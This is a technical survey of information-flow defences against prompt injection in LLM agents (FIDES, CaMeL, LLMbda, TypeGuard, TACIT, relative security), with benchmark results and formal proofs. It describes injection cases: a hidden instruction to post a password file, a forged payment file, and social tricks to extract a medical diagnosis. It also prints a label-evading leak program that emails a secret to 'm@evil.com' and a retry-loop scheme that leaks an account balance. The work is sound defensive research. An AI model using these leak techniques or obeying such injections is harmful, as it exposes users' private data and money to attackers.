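In other words, if someone repeated exactly the same steps with different secrets, the public data would come out the same. Noninterference asks what the agent would really have done with those other secrets, which might be to take another path. If *g1* is the effect of the path it takes on *d1* and *g2* the effect of the path it takes on *d2*, the difference is one subscript:

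```
explicit secrecy:    g1(d1) =L g1(d2)
noninterference:     g1(d1) =L g2(d2)
```

Suppose a patient asks an agent to look at a private test result and, if it is abnormal, to write "appointment needed" in a diary that the whole office can see. The path for an abnormal result writes the same two words whatever the secret is, and the path for a normal result writes nothing. Each path satisfies explicit secrecy on its own, but anyone who opens the diary learns the result through an implicit flow. A strict confidentiality policy might well block the diary entry, because the model wrote it after reading the result. But if the result is normal, the agent makes no tool call for the harness to check, and the missing entry also reveals information.

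The proof also leaves out side channels such as timing and the length of network packets.

Costa and colleagues rejected noninterference as too restrictive. They argue that it would essentially bar an agent from running any tool that may write public data once it has run a tool that may read a secret. An assistant that had looked at its user's private calendar could not then post a public message in the same session. They point out that web browsers and TaintDroid, a privacy monitor for phones, also settled on the weaker property. The argument is convincing for an agent whose decisions all happen inside a model, where the harness can't determine which of them depended on the secret. It is weaker for a design such as CaMeL, whose branches are in a program the harness can read.

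### Results on AgentDojo

The original tests, a 2025 baseline, used GPT-4o and assumed that the attacker knew which tools the agent had. Without policies, 152 injections actually succeeded against the basic agent and 21 against FIDES, whose planner could still inspect a variable and follow instructions it found there. With policies, none succeeded against either. The basic agent does as well as FIDES here because the policy check provides the security, while FIDES uses variables to preserve utility.

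The test's setup almost guaranteed the result of zero. AgentDojo has no labels, so Costa and colleagues marked a field as untrusted if any of the benchmark's attacks used it, whereas an operator has to label data without knowing where attacks will come from. Costa and colleagues also excluded attacks whose goals the policies allowed, such as creating a calendar event with no participants, and attacks that only changed the text of the answer, such as making the agent recommend a certain place to visit. Both exclusions are reasonable for a test of the policies, but a user who follows such a recommendation has still been influenced by the attack.

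The utility figures are more informative. They give the percentage of user tasks completed without an attack, and the last row weights each setting by its number of tasks:

| Setting | GPT-4o, basic | GPT-4o, basic with policies | GPT-4o, FIDES with policies | o1, basic | o1, basic with policies | o1, FIDES with policies |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 75.0 | 37.0 | 59.0 | 70.0 | 48.0 | 64.5 |
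| Travel | 70.0 | 73.0 | 41.0 | 82.0 | 75.0 | 68.0 |
| Banking | 98.8 | 37.5 | 52.5 | 96.2 | 37.5 | 56.2 |
| Slack | 93.3 | 20.0 | 47.6 | 87.6 | 17.1 | 54.3 |
| All tasks | 81.9 | 40.8 | 51.7 | 80.6 | 45.1 | 61.6 |

With GPT-4o, adding policies to the basic agent halved the number of tasks it completed, and FIDES recovered about a quarter of the loss. With o1, a reasoning model, FIDES recovered nearly half. The exception was travel, where many tasks need only tools that the policies allow in an untrusted context. There, the policies didn't reduce the number of tasks the basic agent completed, while FIDES did worse because GPT-4o tended to confuse variable names.

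Some of the remaining loss is deliberate, because many banking tasks ask the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it, which the policy is meant to prevent. If FIDES completed every data-independent task and no others, it would score 79%, so o1 still scored well below what the policies allow.

The agent also completed some tasks by luck. One task was to change the user's password if there was a suspicious transaction. The planner saw the amounts and dates, which counted as trusted, and treated a large payment as suspicious without reading its description. This broke no policy, and the benchmark marked the task as complete.

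Two other groups have measured how much such policies reduce utility, the share of tasks an agent completes. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) applied FIDES's policy to AgentDojo's built-in GPT-4o agent, using an external monitor that left the agent's own loop unchanged. Utility fell from 79.0% to 32.2%, a little below the basic agent's 40.8% in the original tests. Attacks succeeded in 1.0% of runs, down from 25.2%, and the remaining successes involved the agent's final answer, which the monitor didn't check. A different policy blocked attacks about equally well, and the agent still completed 57.3% of tasks. That policy checked whether the user had asked for the action and where its target came from, so it could allow an action even if the context contained untrusted text. This suggests that much of the lost utility comes from judging the whole context at once.

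The other comparison shows how much utility an agent can lose by checking arguments, which FIDES's tested policies mostly didn't do. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) describes an agent that makes a complete plan and then checks the labels of all the values in it. Turning those checks on cut AgentDojo utility from 53.0% to 29.0%, mainly because they rejected plans that passed untrusted tool results to sensitive actions. An agent that used such checks to close the gap in Willison's example would probably lose a similar amount of utility.

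### Later models and human approval

Microsoft's follow-up, *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* by Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), argues that the usual comparison is unfair to FIDES because it sets a defended agent that may never break a policy against an undefended agent that may do anything. Real products often ask the user before a consequential action, so the follow-up counts those requests against an agent. Its basic agent asks before every consequential call, while the labelled agents ask only when a call would violate a policy.

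The newest model in these tests was GPT-5. On AgentDojo without attacks, it gave these results:

| Agent | Tasks completed with no approvals | With at most one approval per task | With unlimited approvals | Total approvals on completed tasks |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Basic | 35.1% | 63.2% | 72.3% | 52.0 |
| Basic with labels | 43.4% | 66.2% | 72.3% | 40.4 |
| FIDES | 57.1% | 72.7% | 78.9% | 41.3 |
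| Prudentia | 72.7% | 79.5% | 80.0% | 7.3 |

By this measure, FIDES completes far more tasks without approval than an agent that has to ask about everything. This benefits only people who would otherwise have been asked for approval. For someone who already lets an ordinary agent run without approvals, switching to FIDES would reduce completion from 72.3% to 57.1%. FIDES needed about as many approvals in total as the basic agent with labels, but it completed more tasks.

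Prudentia, the follow-up's new agent, uses the same labels and checks as FIDES but tells the planner about them. Before inspecting a variable, the planner has to explain why it needs to and which calls it will make afterwards. It can also ask the user to endorse a piece of text. If an email lists ten tasks that each need a consequential call, FIDES would need ten approvals after reading it, whereas Prudentia can ask the user once to treat the email as trusted and then carry out all ten.

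That convenience is risky because, if the user overlooks an injection in the email, the harness will also treat every call that follows from it as trusted. The experiments can't measure how often this would happen, because they used harmless data and assumed that a person would approve every request on a task the agent completed. Kolluri and colleagues leave the design of clearer approval requests to future work.

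Prudentia also seems to need a capable planner. With GPT-4o, it completed 42.5% of tasks without approvals, while FIDES completed 50.3%. It uses many more tokens too, and an average banking task with GPT-4o cost 3.86 cents for Prudentia, compared with 1.54 cents for FIDES and 0.38 cents for the basic agent with labels. The experimenters had not tried to reduce these costs.

When a call fails a check, the harness in *APPA* (2026) searches a set of registered policy changes for a permitted way to continue, instead of relying on the planner to avoid blocked calls.

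### Labels in released software

Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (May 2026) announced FIDES as an experimental feature of Agent Framework, a toolkit for building agents. Its example is an agent that sorts bug reports on GitHub. A public report contains a hidden instruction to read a file of passwords and post the contents as a comment. The model may follow the instruction and read the file. The file's contents are private, so the context becomes private too. The tool for posting comments accepts only public data, so the harness blocks the comment or asks a person to review it.

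The guarantee depends on the labels being correct. This release treats a tool as trusted and public if the developer forgets to label it, which removes protection without warning. Microsoft acknowledges this and has asked developers whether the default should be stricter.

Even careful labels involve guesses. Microsoft's post on secure, autonomous agents says that its GitHub labels mark files and issues from public repositories as untrusted and those from private repositories as trusted. This is a sensible default, but if a colleague pastes a customer's email into a private issue, the harness will label the customer's text as trusted.

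### The FLOWSEAL dispute

Shim, Karim and colleagues argue in *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (September 2026) that the language model performs all of FIDES's policy enforcement, so an attacker who confuses the model can get past that enforcement. Their paper is about another labelling system, FLOWSEAL.

FIDES's published algorithm contradicts this. The planning loop, which is ordinary code, computes the labels and checks the policy before it runs a tool. The model's reply is an input to that check, but the model cannot skip the check or lower a label. The released software also has a component that inspects each call before the tool runs. Girrens and Wang likewise describe FIDES as checking every call against the labels and blocking violations. The planner decides which variables to inspect, but a bad decision only makes its context less trusted and its later calls more restricted.

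Shim and colleagues did not run FIDES, explaining that it was designed for a different purpose and that they could not integrate it with their benchmarks. FLOWSEAL itself relies on a model at a more sensitive point. Its code intercepts every outgoing call, but when the labels alone would block a call to an unknown recipient, a separate language model compares the message with the protected records and classifies it as "safe" or "blocked". The paper's confidentiality theorem therefore does not cover cases where this model wrongly classifies a message as "safe". In the tests, FLOWSEAL leaked between 0% and 3.3% of the sensitive items. It also completed 72.4% of harmless tasks, probably in part because the second model can let a harmless message through after the agent has read a secret.

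The attacks in the paper are still a good test for FIDES because they contain no injected commands. In the running example, Jane's agent holds Mark's medical diagnosis, and Mark's former wife Emily wants it. Emily sets up a shared page with a blank section for Jane's notes and asks the agent to fill it in. FIDES's confidentiality policy should block this, since Emily can read the page but isn't permitted to read the diagnosis. The looser rule from the AgentDojo tests requires only that the call be trusted, so the outcome would depend on how the harness labels Emily's message. If it arrives as an email from an outsider, it is untrusted and the call fails. But FIDES assumes that the user, here Jane, is honest, so the call goes through if the harness passes Emily's message to the planner as a user's request.

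In another attack, Emily asks the agent to delete the false statements from a page of true and false statements about Mark's health. The agent writes nothing secret, but Emily can learn the truth from the statements that remain. FIDES's tested policy for deleting files and emails checks only whether the call is trusted, and a similar rule for this page would allow the deletions if Emily's request counted as trusted. Explicit secrecy also permits this leak, because the secret determines which deletions happen and not what any of them writes.

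## LLMbda: a noninterference proof for a whole agent language

FIDES's guarantee doesn't cover leaks like Emily's, in which a secret determines which actions happen. CaMeL's strict mode should do better because it also labels what happens inside a branch, but in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) found a way to leak a secret past those labels. They then designed LLMbda, a small programming language for agents, and proved a form of noninterference for every program in it.

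### An assignment that never runs

Suppose an agent manages a customer's bank account, and an attacker wants to know whether the balance is above some threshold. The obvious program fails:

```
if balance > threshold: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

The condition reads the balance, so CaMeL gives the branch a secret label and blocks the email. With two extra variables, the program gets the same fact out:

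```
tmp  = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

The table follows both possible runs:

| Line | Balance above threshold | Balance at or below threshold |
|---|---|---|
| `tmp = True` | `tmp` is True, public | `tmp` is True, public |
| `rich = True` | `rich` is True, public | `rich` is True, public |
| `if balance > threshold: tmp = False` | runs; `tmp` is False, secret | skipped; `tmp` stays True, public |
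| `if tmp: rich = False` | skipped; `rich` stays True, public | runs; `rich` is False, public |
| `if rich: send_email(...)` | runs; the email goes out | skipped; no email |

The variable `rich` is public at the end of both runs, yet its value reveals the secret. In the first run, `rich` stays True only because the secret variable `tmp` is False. CaMeL still labels `rich` public because it raises a variable's label only when it executes an assignment to that variable, and this run never executes `rich = False`. A monitor that follows a single run can't update labels based on assignments that the run skips.

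The trick goes back to Fenton's work on memoryless subsystems. Fenton's machine was not vulnerable to it because each register had a fixed label. The machine would have skipped `tmp = False` because it changes a public register from inside a secret branch, and both runs would have ended the same way. CaMeL's labels change as the program runs, which makes the trick possible.

The program is contrived. CaMeL's planner writes its code before any model reads untrusted data, so an attacker would need some other way to get this code written, such as a request that the user copied from a web page. Even so, a public label in CaMeL doesn't prove that a value is independent of secrets.

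### A retry loop without labels

When a program fails, CaMeL tries again through a loop written in ordinary Python, outside the interpreter. Each attempt starts with clean labels, even though it depends on error messages from the previous one. CaMeL censors those messages, but whether a policy blocked the previous attempt may itself depend on a secret.

That fact reveals one bit, and most information-flow systems tolerate a leak of about that size per run, but a loop can repeat the leak. Suppose a program breaks a policy only if the balance is above a chosen number, and the loop sets the next number according to whether the last attempt failed. Twenty attempts could then identify any whole-dollar balance up to about a million, since 2^20 is 1,048,576. The interpreter may handle each attempt correctly, but it doesn't track the information that accumulates across attempts.

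Garby and colleagues also found that CaMeL treats an untrusted value as trusted once a program inserts it into a string literal. This is an ordinary bug and probably easy to fix. It was hard to notice because CaMeL's labelling rules are defined only by the Python code that implements them.

### Labels on values, branches and conversations

LLMbda, pronounced "L-L-Em-da", extends the lambda calculus, a minimal language that builds programs entirely out of functions. It adds commands for holding a conversation with a model. A program can send a prompt and receive a reply, and if the reply is code, the program can run it. `fork` does some work in a temporary copy of the conversation and then discards the copy, while `clear` empties the conversation. With these, a programmer can write Willison's quarantined model as a short function:

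```
quarantine(prompt) = fork ( clear; ask(prompt) )
```

CaMeL and FIDES build the two-model design into their architecture, whereas an LLMbda program can use it, change it or leave it out, and the proof covers all three cases.

Every value in LLMbda has a label, and so does the branch that the program is currently in. Anything the program computes in a secret branch becomes secret. The conversation also has a label, which is the join of the labels on everything sent to the model. If the model replies with code, that code runs as if it were inside a branch with the conversation's label. So if the model writes code after reading a stranger's email, everything that code computes is untrusted.

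The language has no assignment statement, which removes Fenton's trick for variables. An `if` returns a value whichever side runs, and the label of that value always includes the label of the condition:

```
tmp  = if balance > threshold then False else True     secret in both runs
rich = if tmp then False else True                     secret in both runs
```

The conversation does change as a program runs, however, so it needs a rule of its own. Consider this program, which tries to use the model's context as the variable:

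```
ask("Remember this value: x = false")
if secret: ask("Set x = true")
ask("Give me the value of x")
```

When `secret` is true, the second line would write to a public conversation from a secret branch. LLMbda stops the program with an error, following a rule known as no-high-upgrade, which forbids writing to the conversation from a branch whose label is more restrictive than the conversation's. If the interpreter instead raised the conversation's label to secret at that point, the secret would still leak when `secret` is false, because the second line never runs, the conversation stays public, and the model's answer reveals the value.

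Stopping the program still reveals information about `secret`, because the program finishes only if `secret` is false. LLMbda allows this leak, which Fenton's silent skipping avoided, but its main theorem bounds how much the leak can reveal.

### Termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference

Random sampling by the language model and programs that may stop early or run forever both complicate noninterference. LLMbda's theorem handles both using a property called termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference (TIPNI).

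Suppose an agent would answer "yes" with probability 0.7 and "no" with probability 0.3, whatever the secret is. Sometimes it stops before the answer gets out, and the secret affects when that happens:

| Outcome | Secret is A | Secret is B | If it always finished (*ω*) |
|---|---|---|---|
| "yes" | 0.70 | 0.50 | 0.70 |
| "no" | 0.20 | 0.30 | 0.30 |
| Does not finish | 0.10 | 0.20 | 0 |

The first two columns differ, so exact noninterference fails. But both could come from the last column if some runs simply failed to finish. TIPNI calls two such sets of probabilities compatible, and it requires compatibility where exact noninterference requires equality. Let *μ0* and *μ1* give the probabilities of each visible outcome *q* from two starting points:

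```
if the two starting points differ only in data the observer cannot see,
then there is an ω such that
     μ0(q) ≤ ω(q)  and  μ1(q) ≤ ω(q)   for every visible outcome q,
     and the values of ω add up to at most 1
```

A starting point consists of a program and its conversation. The secret may affect whether the program finishes but may not otherwise affect the visible result.

Garby and colleagues first defined noninterference by comparing only the runs that finish, but this turned out to be the wrong definition. In the example, "yes" makes up 78% of the finished runs with secret A and 62.5% with secret B. The agent would fail that definition even though the secret affects only when the agent stops.

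Compatibility also limits how far apart the visible results can be. Measure the distance between *μ0* and *μ1* as half the sum of their differences over all visible outcomes. Since *ω* is at least as large as both, the larger of the two probabilities, summed over every outcome, can't exceed 1. The larger of any two numbers is their average plus half their difference. If the runs fail to finish with probability 0.1 and 0.2, the visible outcomes sum to 0.9 and 0.8, so:

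```
(0.9 + 0.8) / 2  +  distance  ≤  1
                    distance  ≤  0.15
```

This is always the average of the two failure probabilities. The example reaches the limit exactly, because half of (0.20 + 0.10) is 0.15.

The limit is useful only if programs usually finish. If both runs always finish, the limit is zero and the visible probabilities must be equal. But a run that a policy stops counts as unfinished, so if policies stopped half of all runs, the visible probabilities could differ by as much as 0.5. The distance also doesn't account for whether a run finished, so an observer who can see that the agent has stopped may learn more.

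Garby and colleagues put the retry loop inside the language, so it has labels like everything else, and a program can't catch its own policy violations and carry on. But a person or scheduled job that reruns a blocked agent is still outside the language and could recreate the leak from CaMeL's loop.

### A proof that skips the protected work

Finding a suitable *ω* for one program is easy, but the theorem needs one for every program. Garby and colleagues construct it by defining a second way to run a program. As soon as a computation's label rises above what the observer may see, this version abandons the computation and substitutes an empty value. They then prove three facts:

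1. The skipping version reaches each visible outcome at least as often as the real program. The skipped work could not have changed anything visible, so its only possible effect was to prevent the program from finishing.
2. From two starting points that differ only in protected data, the skipping version produces the same probabilities, because it never computes on that data.
3. Those probabilities add up to at most 1.

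If *ω0* and *ω1* are the skipping version's results from the two starting points, the facts combine into one line:

```
μ0  ≤  ω0  =  ω1  ≥  μ1
```

Smith and Alpízar's earlier proof technique deleted the protected parts from the program's text before running it. That can't work when a model writes some of the program during the run, so LLMbda's proof has to skip each protected part as execution reaches it.

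The proofs are written in Lean, a programming language that can also check mathematical proofs. The interpreter is also written in Lean, and another theorem shows that it produces each result with the probability specified by the language's definition. The proofs therefore cover the harness that calls the model, except for the network code that fetches each reply.

### Endorsement and why secrets stay protected

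An agent that never trusted anything derived from an email would be of little use, so LLMbda has an `endorse` command that marks untrusted data as trusted. Suppose an agent must acknowledge an email and put its category in the subject line. A quarantined model picks the category, so the category is untrusted, and the email tool rejects untrusted subjects. The program can replace the category with the matching entry from a fixed list and then endorse that entry. If the list has eight entries, the sender of the original email can influence the subject by at most three bits and can't insert their own text.

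`endorse` changes only one half of a label:

```
before:   (untrusted, secret)
after:    (trusted,   secret)
```

The secrecy guarantee survives endorsement because secrecy and integrity are independent. Endorsing a value does not change whether it is visible to an observer who can see public data, however untrustworthy, but not secret data. Garby and colleagues prove that TIPNI holds for every such observer, whatever an attacker puts in the untrusted data and whatever the program endorses. They call this version insulated. Swapping secrecy and integrity gives the matching result that the integrity guarantee survives declassification.

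The integrity guarantee does not hold with `endorse`, whose purpose is to let untrusted data through. However, an endorsed value can't become more trusted than the branch it is in. If a model writes code after reading an attacker's text, that code runs in an untrusted branch, so any `endorse` in it has no effect.

An attacker can bypass this restriction if the program has already endorsed the text. The model's code then runs as trusted, and its own endorsements take effect. The paper suggests permanently marking every endorsed value and refusing to endorse a marked value again. Programmers can do this without changing the language, so the existing proofs still apply, but Garby and colleagues have not yet defined precisely what protection it adds.

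### What the theorem assumes

Like FIDES, LLMbda relies on correct labels for incoming data. Its tools also need the right checks. In one of the paper's examples, an agent finds a sender's address in an email and sends a reminder there. The email tool checks that the subject and body are trusted, so the theorem guarantees that injected text can't affect either. The tool doesn't check the recipient, which is untrusted because it came from the email. An attacker could therefore redirect the message without violating the theorem, as in Willison's example of the document for Bob.

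Garby and colleagues acknowledge a third assumption, that all tools and data sources are inside the program. Their bank is a record that the program passes from function to function, and sending money means returning an updated record. A real bank makes the payment immediately. The difference matters because the theorem is about final results. Suppose an agent with real tools posts the numbers 1, 2, 3 and so on to a public page, and a policy stops it when it reaches a secret number. Anyone reading the page learns the secret from the last post, but in LLMbda's model the run never finishes and so produces no visible result.

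### Randori, an agent that practises first

To test the language on realistic tasks, Garby and colleagues used it to write an agent called Randori, which follows the same broad plan as CaMeL.

Randori is named for how it handles retries. If a program fails on real data, the error message depends on that data, so any program the planner writes after reading it would be untrusted. Randori instead tests programs in a practice phase with made-up data, where payments do nothing and every file contains the same placeholder text. The planner revises its program until it runs without an error, then writes a final version that the harness runs once on the real data. This makes retrying safe, but the planner can't fix problems that appear only in the real run. These include policy violations, because the practice phase doesn't check labels.

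The test was AgentDojo's banking setting. Each agent had three attempts at each of the 16 user tasks without an attack, or 48 runs, and three at each of the 144 task-attack pairs. Garby and colleagues also reran CaMeL on two of the same models. Some of CaMeL's attacked runs did not complete, and the table leaves those out:

| Agent | Model | Tasks completed, no attack | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
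| Randori | GPT-5.2 | 36 of 48 | 2 of 432 |
| Randori | Qwen3.7-plus | 36 of 48 | 0 of 432 |
| Randori | MiMo-v2.5 | 31 of 48 | 0 of 432 |
| Randori without endorsement | Qwen3.7-plus | 30 of 48 | 0 of 432 |
| Randori without endorsement | MiMo-v2.5 | 26 of 48 | 0 of 432 |
| CaMeL without policies | GPT-5.2 | 32 of 48 | 1 of 240 |
| CaMeL without policies | MiMo-v2.5 | 34 of 48 | 4 of 382 |
| CaMeL with policies | GPT-5.2 | 18 of 48 | 0 of 231 |
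| CaMeL with policies | MiMo-v2.5 | 18 of 48 | 0 of 357 |

Randori completed about as many tasks as CaMeL did with its policies off, and about twice as many as with them on. These figures are imprecise because there were only 16 different tasks. With GPT-5.2, Randori completed 75% of tasks, with a 95% interval of about 56% to 94%.

Randori also enforces only a subset of CaMeL's policies, so the two systems aren't directly comparable. For example, Randori's tool for scheduling a payment requires a trusted amount but not a trusted recipient. Endorsement explains only part of Randori's advantage. With MiMo-v2.5 and no endorsement, Randori still completed 26 runs to CaMeL's 18, probably in part because its policies are looser. The results show that an agent can do useful work in a language with a noninterference proof, but not that the proof lets an agent do more useful work under strict policies.

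### Which attacks test the labels

Garby and colleagues divide the 144 pairs by whether a plan for the user's task could contain the tool call that the attack needs. In 97 of them, the plan would never contain that call, as when the attack needs a payment but the user wants a summary of recent transactions. Planning before reading generally stops these attacks without any labels. In the other 47 pairs, the plan may contain the call, so the outcome can depend on enforcement.

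About two-thirds of the 144 pairs in the security score therefore test the architecture, and the remaining third test the labels only weakly. With its policies off, CaMeL resisted the attacks in all 141 runs on that remaining third with GPT-5.2, and in 138 with MiMo-v2.5. Because these attacks rarely succeed even without enforcement, a near-perfect score with enforcement reveals little about how much the enforcement contributed.

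Planning first also failed once with each model when CaMeL's policies were off. The user had asked the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The planner wrote a loop that read each instruction and called whichever tool it named, so plan integrity gave no protection.

### Paying as the file instructs

Both successful attacks on Randori used the same user task and injection. The user asks the agent to read a text file and make the payment it describes, but the attacker has replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. Randori's planner endorsed the payment details, as the task required, and the agent paid the attacker in two of three attempts with GPT-5.2.

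Without endorsement, the labels would block this attack, but they would also block the payment the user wanted. Three of the 16 tasks ask the agent to act on a file's contents in this way, and they account for most of what the agent loses when it can't endorse. A genuine bill and a forged one from the same file have the same label, so the agent would have to tell them apart by judging whether the text looks suspicious, which is the kind of probabilistic defence that labels were supposed to replace.

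CaMeL's evaluation had a successful attack of the same kind, which its developers place outside their threat model. Garby and colleagues argue that the same kind of attack still succeeded against four systems, including FIDES and TACIT, and that this marks a limit of information-flow defences. But FIDES and TACIT share a different case, in which the agent quotes a hotel review and the benchmark counts the quotation as a successful attack. The payment case is enough to support the argument without them, because the user explicitly asked for the file to determine who gets paid.

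### Borrowing a type system

Because LLMbda is new, no model has been trained on much of it, so Randori's planner has to learn the syntax from its prompt. Two other groups instead have the model write in an existing language and rely on that language's type checker, the part of the compiler that rejects programs that use the wrong kind of value.

Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova (2026), in *Language-Based Agent Control*, use Haskell, whose types record what effects a program may have as well as what data it returns. Their system is named TypeGuard in the first version of the paper and ELBA in a later revision. A developer states the type that the model's program must have, and the harness runs only programs of that type. For a calculator, that type might be a plain integer. If someone asks the calculator to delete every file on the server and then compute a factorial, the model may well write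 a program that does so, but the harness won't run it because a plain integer type doesn't allow a program to delete files.

Types can also restrict where data comes from. In another example, an agent compiles a bibliography and may write only records that it fetched from DBLP, a database of computer science papers. The fetching function returns a `Trusted` record, the writing function accepts only `Trusted` records, and the model's code cannot create one any other way. Over 100 tasks, none of this agent's 925 citations were false, compared with 19 of 1,002 from an ordinary agent with a search tool.

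TypeGuard uses LIO, an existing Haskell library, to check secrecy and integrity labels as the program runs. The label rises with everything the program reads, so the agent faces the same label creep as FIDES. A program can limit this by having a sub-agent do the reading in an isolated computation. Unlike a quarantined model, the sub-agent can use tools, subject to the same policies. For instance, it could fetch a web page, draft a message about it, and return the draft as a labelled value that the main agent hasn't read.

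The model can also read a result and then write more code, which CaMeL's planner can't do. This flexibility did little to reduce the number of tasks lost to strict policies. In the first version of the paper, with GPT-5.4 on AgentDojo's Slack setting, policies reduced the number of completed tasks from 15 of 21 to 8 for TypeGuard and from 15 to 7 for CaMeL. In the revision, which tested four models, the new system with policies completed 8 to 10 tasks, compared with 4 to 6 for CaMeL, but took about three times as long.

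Zhou and colleagues give clearer evidence than the banking tests that enforcement has an effect. The standard attacks never succeeded against their revised system, even with its policies off, but in a separate adversarial evaluation without policies it resisted only 57.8% to 84.5% of injections, depending on the model. With policies on, it resisted all of them. The benchmark had counted 29 attacks in the runs with policies as successful because the agent visited a certain web address, but manual review found no violation in any.

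Zhou and colleagues also prove that any property Haskell's type system guarantees for ordinary programs still holds when a program calls an agent. The guarantee is only as strong as what the language and its libraries provide. Unlike LLMbda, neither TypeGuard nor the second system, TACIT, has a machine-checked proof about the complete agent.

TACIT, which Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026) present in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, uses Scala 3. Its central idea is the capability, a value that a program must hold in order to do something, such as open a file or contact a server. Scala can record in a function's type which capabilities the function uses. TACIT wraps secret data in a container called `Classified`, and the only functions that the agent's code may apply to the contents are those that use no capabilities:

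```
secret.map(text => text.toUpperCase)      allowed; the result stays wrapped
secret.map(text => file.write(text))      rejected before the program runs
```

If the agent prints a classified value, the user sees the contents but the model receives only asterisks. A separate trusted model can summarise classified text, and its summary stays in the container.

Odersky and colleagues tested this on a software project with a folder of secrets. Some of the 131 trials for each model contained injections, and in 11 the user's own request was hostile. With the container, neither Claude Sonnet 4.6 nor MiniMax M2.5 leaked anything. Without it, MiniMax leaked secrets in eight of the 11 trials with hostile requests and Claude in two. Writing Scala had little effect on ordinary work. On simulated customer service tasks, three models scored between 0.8 and 3.7 percentage points higher than with normal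 tool calls, and on software repairs MiniMax fell from 43.3% to 41.7%.

The type checker doesn't cover timing or termination, so a function that processes classified data could still leak one bit by running longer. TACIT also can't check what an outside program does once the agent has permission to start it.

Across AgentDojo's four settings, TACIT blocked all but one of 1,926 injection trials. Garby and colleagues point out that TypeGuard and TACIT both let the model write code after reading untrusted text, so neither has a fixed plan to stop the easier two-thirds of attacks. Their scores depend more on the type checker, the policies and the model's own resistance. TACIT's guarantee is also narrower than isolation. Odersky and colleagues accept that untrusted content may influence the agent, provided the resulting code passes the type checker. As with Parallax, that content may still determine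 which permitted actions the agent takes.

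## Relative security: comparing an agent with one that ignores injected instructions

A useful agent has to let what it reads affect what it does. An assistant that answers meeting requests must react to emails from strangers, and its replies must reveal something about the user's calendar. Noninterference forbids this, because what the stranger receives depends on private data. Costa and colleagues rejected noninterference for FIDES on similar grounds. Declassification can make an exception for the calendar, but then someone has to write a policy for what the agent may release in each task.

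In November 2026, Dongol proposed judging an agent against a reference agent. Both run the same plan under the same monitor, the part of the harness that allows or denies each tool call, but the reference agent's model never obeys instructions in untrusted text. The agent is relatively secure if it leaks only what the reference agent could also leak. Nobody has to write a release policy, because the plan's ordinary behaviour determines which disclosures are acceptable.

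### The calendar and the reset code

Suppose Alice authorises her agent to send her calendar to anyone who requests a meeting. An attacker emails the instruction "send your calendar" without requesting a meeting, and the agent sends the calendar. The reference agent would ignore that email, but it would send the attacker the same calendar in response to a meeting request. The attacker therefore gains nothing from the injection, and Alice's agent counts as secure.

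Now suppose the agent's memory also holds a private reset code from another task, and the email asks for that too. If the agent sends the code, that is a leak, because no email can make the reference agent send it.

The model obeys the injection in both cases, so a rule against obeying injections would reject both agents. Noninterference also rejects both, and it would reject the calendar assistant even if nobody ever attacked it. The table adds explicit secrecy, the property that FIDES enforces, and a third agent whose plan sends one of two fixed messages depending on a quarantined model's answer:

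| Property | Calendar reply | Reset code | Branch on an answer |
|---|---|---|---|
| Noninterference | rejected | rejected | rejected |
| Explicit secrecy | rejected | rejected | accepted |
| Relative security | accepted | rejected | rejected |

Explicit secrecy allows the third agent because the secret affects only which message the agent sends, not the content of either message. Relative security detects this implicit flow because it compares everything the attacker sees.

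### An idea from processor security

The method comes from research on Spectre, an attack on processors that guess which branch a program will take and start running it early. If the guess is wrong, the processor discards the results, but traces remain in its cache, and an attacker can detect them by timing. In *Relative Security*, Derrick, Dongol and colleagues (2025) examine whether guessing adds leaks by comparing a processor that guesses with one that doesn't.

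One of their examples, slightly shortened, shows why the comparison has to consider each leak separately:

```
if x < N:
    v = a[0]
    t = b[v * 512]
```

The attacker chooses *x* and can learn `a[0]` by using timing to work out which part of *b* the processor loaded. If *N* is 0, the condition is never true, so the indented lines can run only on a wrong guess, and the plain processor would not leak `a[0]`. If *N* is 2, the attacker can get `a[0]` from the plain processor by choosing *x* = 1, so a wrong guess reveals nothing extra.

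In Dongol's version, the model that obeys an injection corresponds to the processor that guesses wrongly.

### What counts as the same leak

A leak always involves two runs, because the question is whether the attacker can tell one secret from another. In simplified notation:

```
leak(r1, r2, s1, s2):
    run r1 has secrets s1, and run r2 has secrets s2
    the attacker sends the same text in both runs
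    the attacker sees different results

relative security:
    if the agent has runs r1, r2 with           leak(r1, r2, s1, s2)
    then the reference has runs v1, v2 with     leak(v1, v2, s1, s2)
```

The reference runs must start with the same memory and trusted inputs as the agent runs they match. The attacker must send the same text in *v1* and *v2*, but it may differ from the text in *r1* and *r2*. A genuine meeting request in the reference runs can therefore justify the agent's response to an injected one.

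That freedom can make the definition too lenient. Suppose the plan lets a stranger guess Alice's four-digit code once and replies "right" or "wrong", but an injection makes the agent send the whole code. The reference agent can also distinguish any two codes if the stranger guesses one of them. For example, guessing 1234 distinguishes 1234 from 5678. Since this works for every pair of codes, the agent counts as relatively secure, even though the injection reveals all four digits and an ordinary run tests only one code out of 10,000.

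Dongol gives a stricter version, called uniform relative security, to rule this out. It requires the reference run's attacker text to be a fixed function of the agent run's attacker text, independent of the secrets. In the example, this means the guess must be the same whatever the code is. The reference agent then gives the same answer for any two codes other than that guess, while the injected agent still tells them apart, so the injected agent fails the stricter version. Someone who cares about how much leaks in a single session needs this version.

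### The fence theorem

A real model follows some injected instructions and not others, and nobody can predict exactly which. Dongol lets the attacker choose which text the model treats as an instruction, which tool the instruction calls, and when the model follows it. The call's arguments may draw on everything in the agent's memory. A proof that covers every such choice does not depend on the model's training.

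Under this assumption, defences that work by persuading the model do not count as protection. Spotlighting, for example, marks untrusted text and asks the model not to follow instructions in it. For any reversible marking, there is a possible model that undoes the marking and obeys the instructions anyway, so Dongol concludes that spotlighting leaks. This means that spotlighting offers no guarantee, but it does not show how often spotlighting fails in practice.

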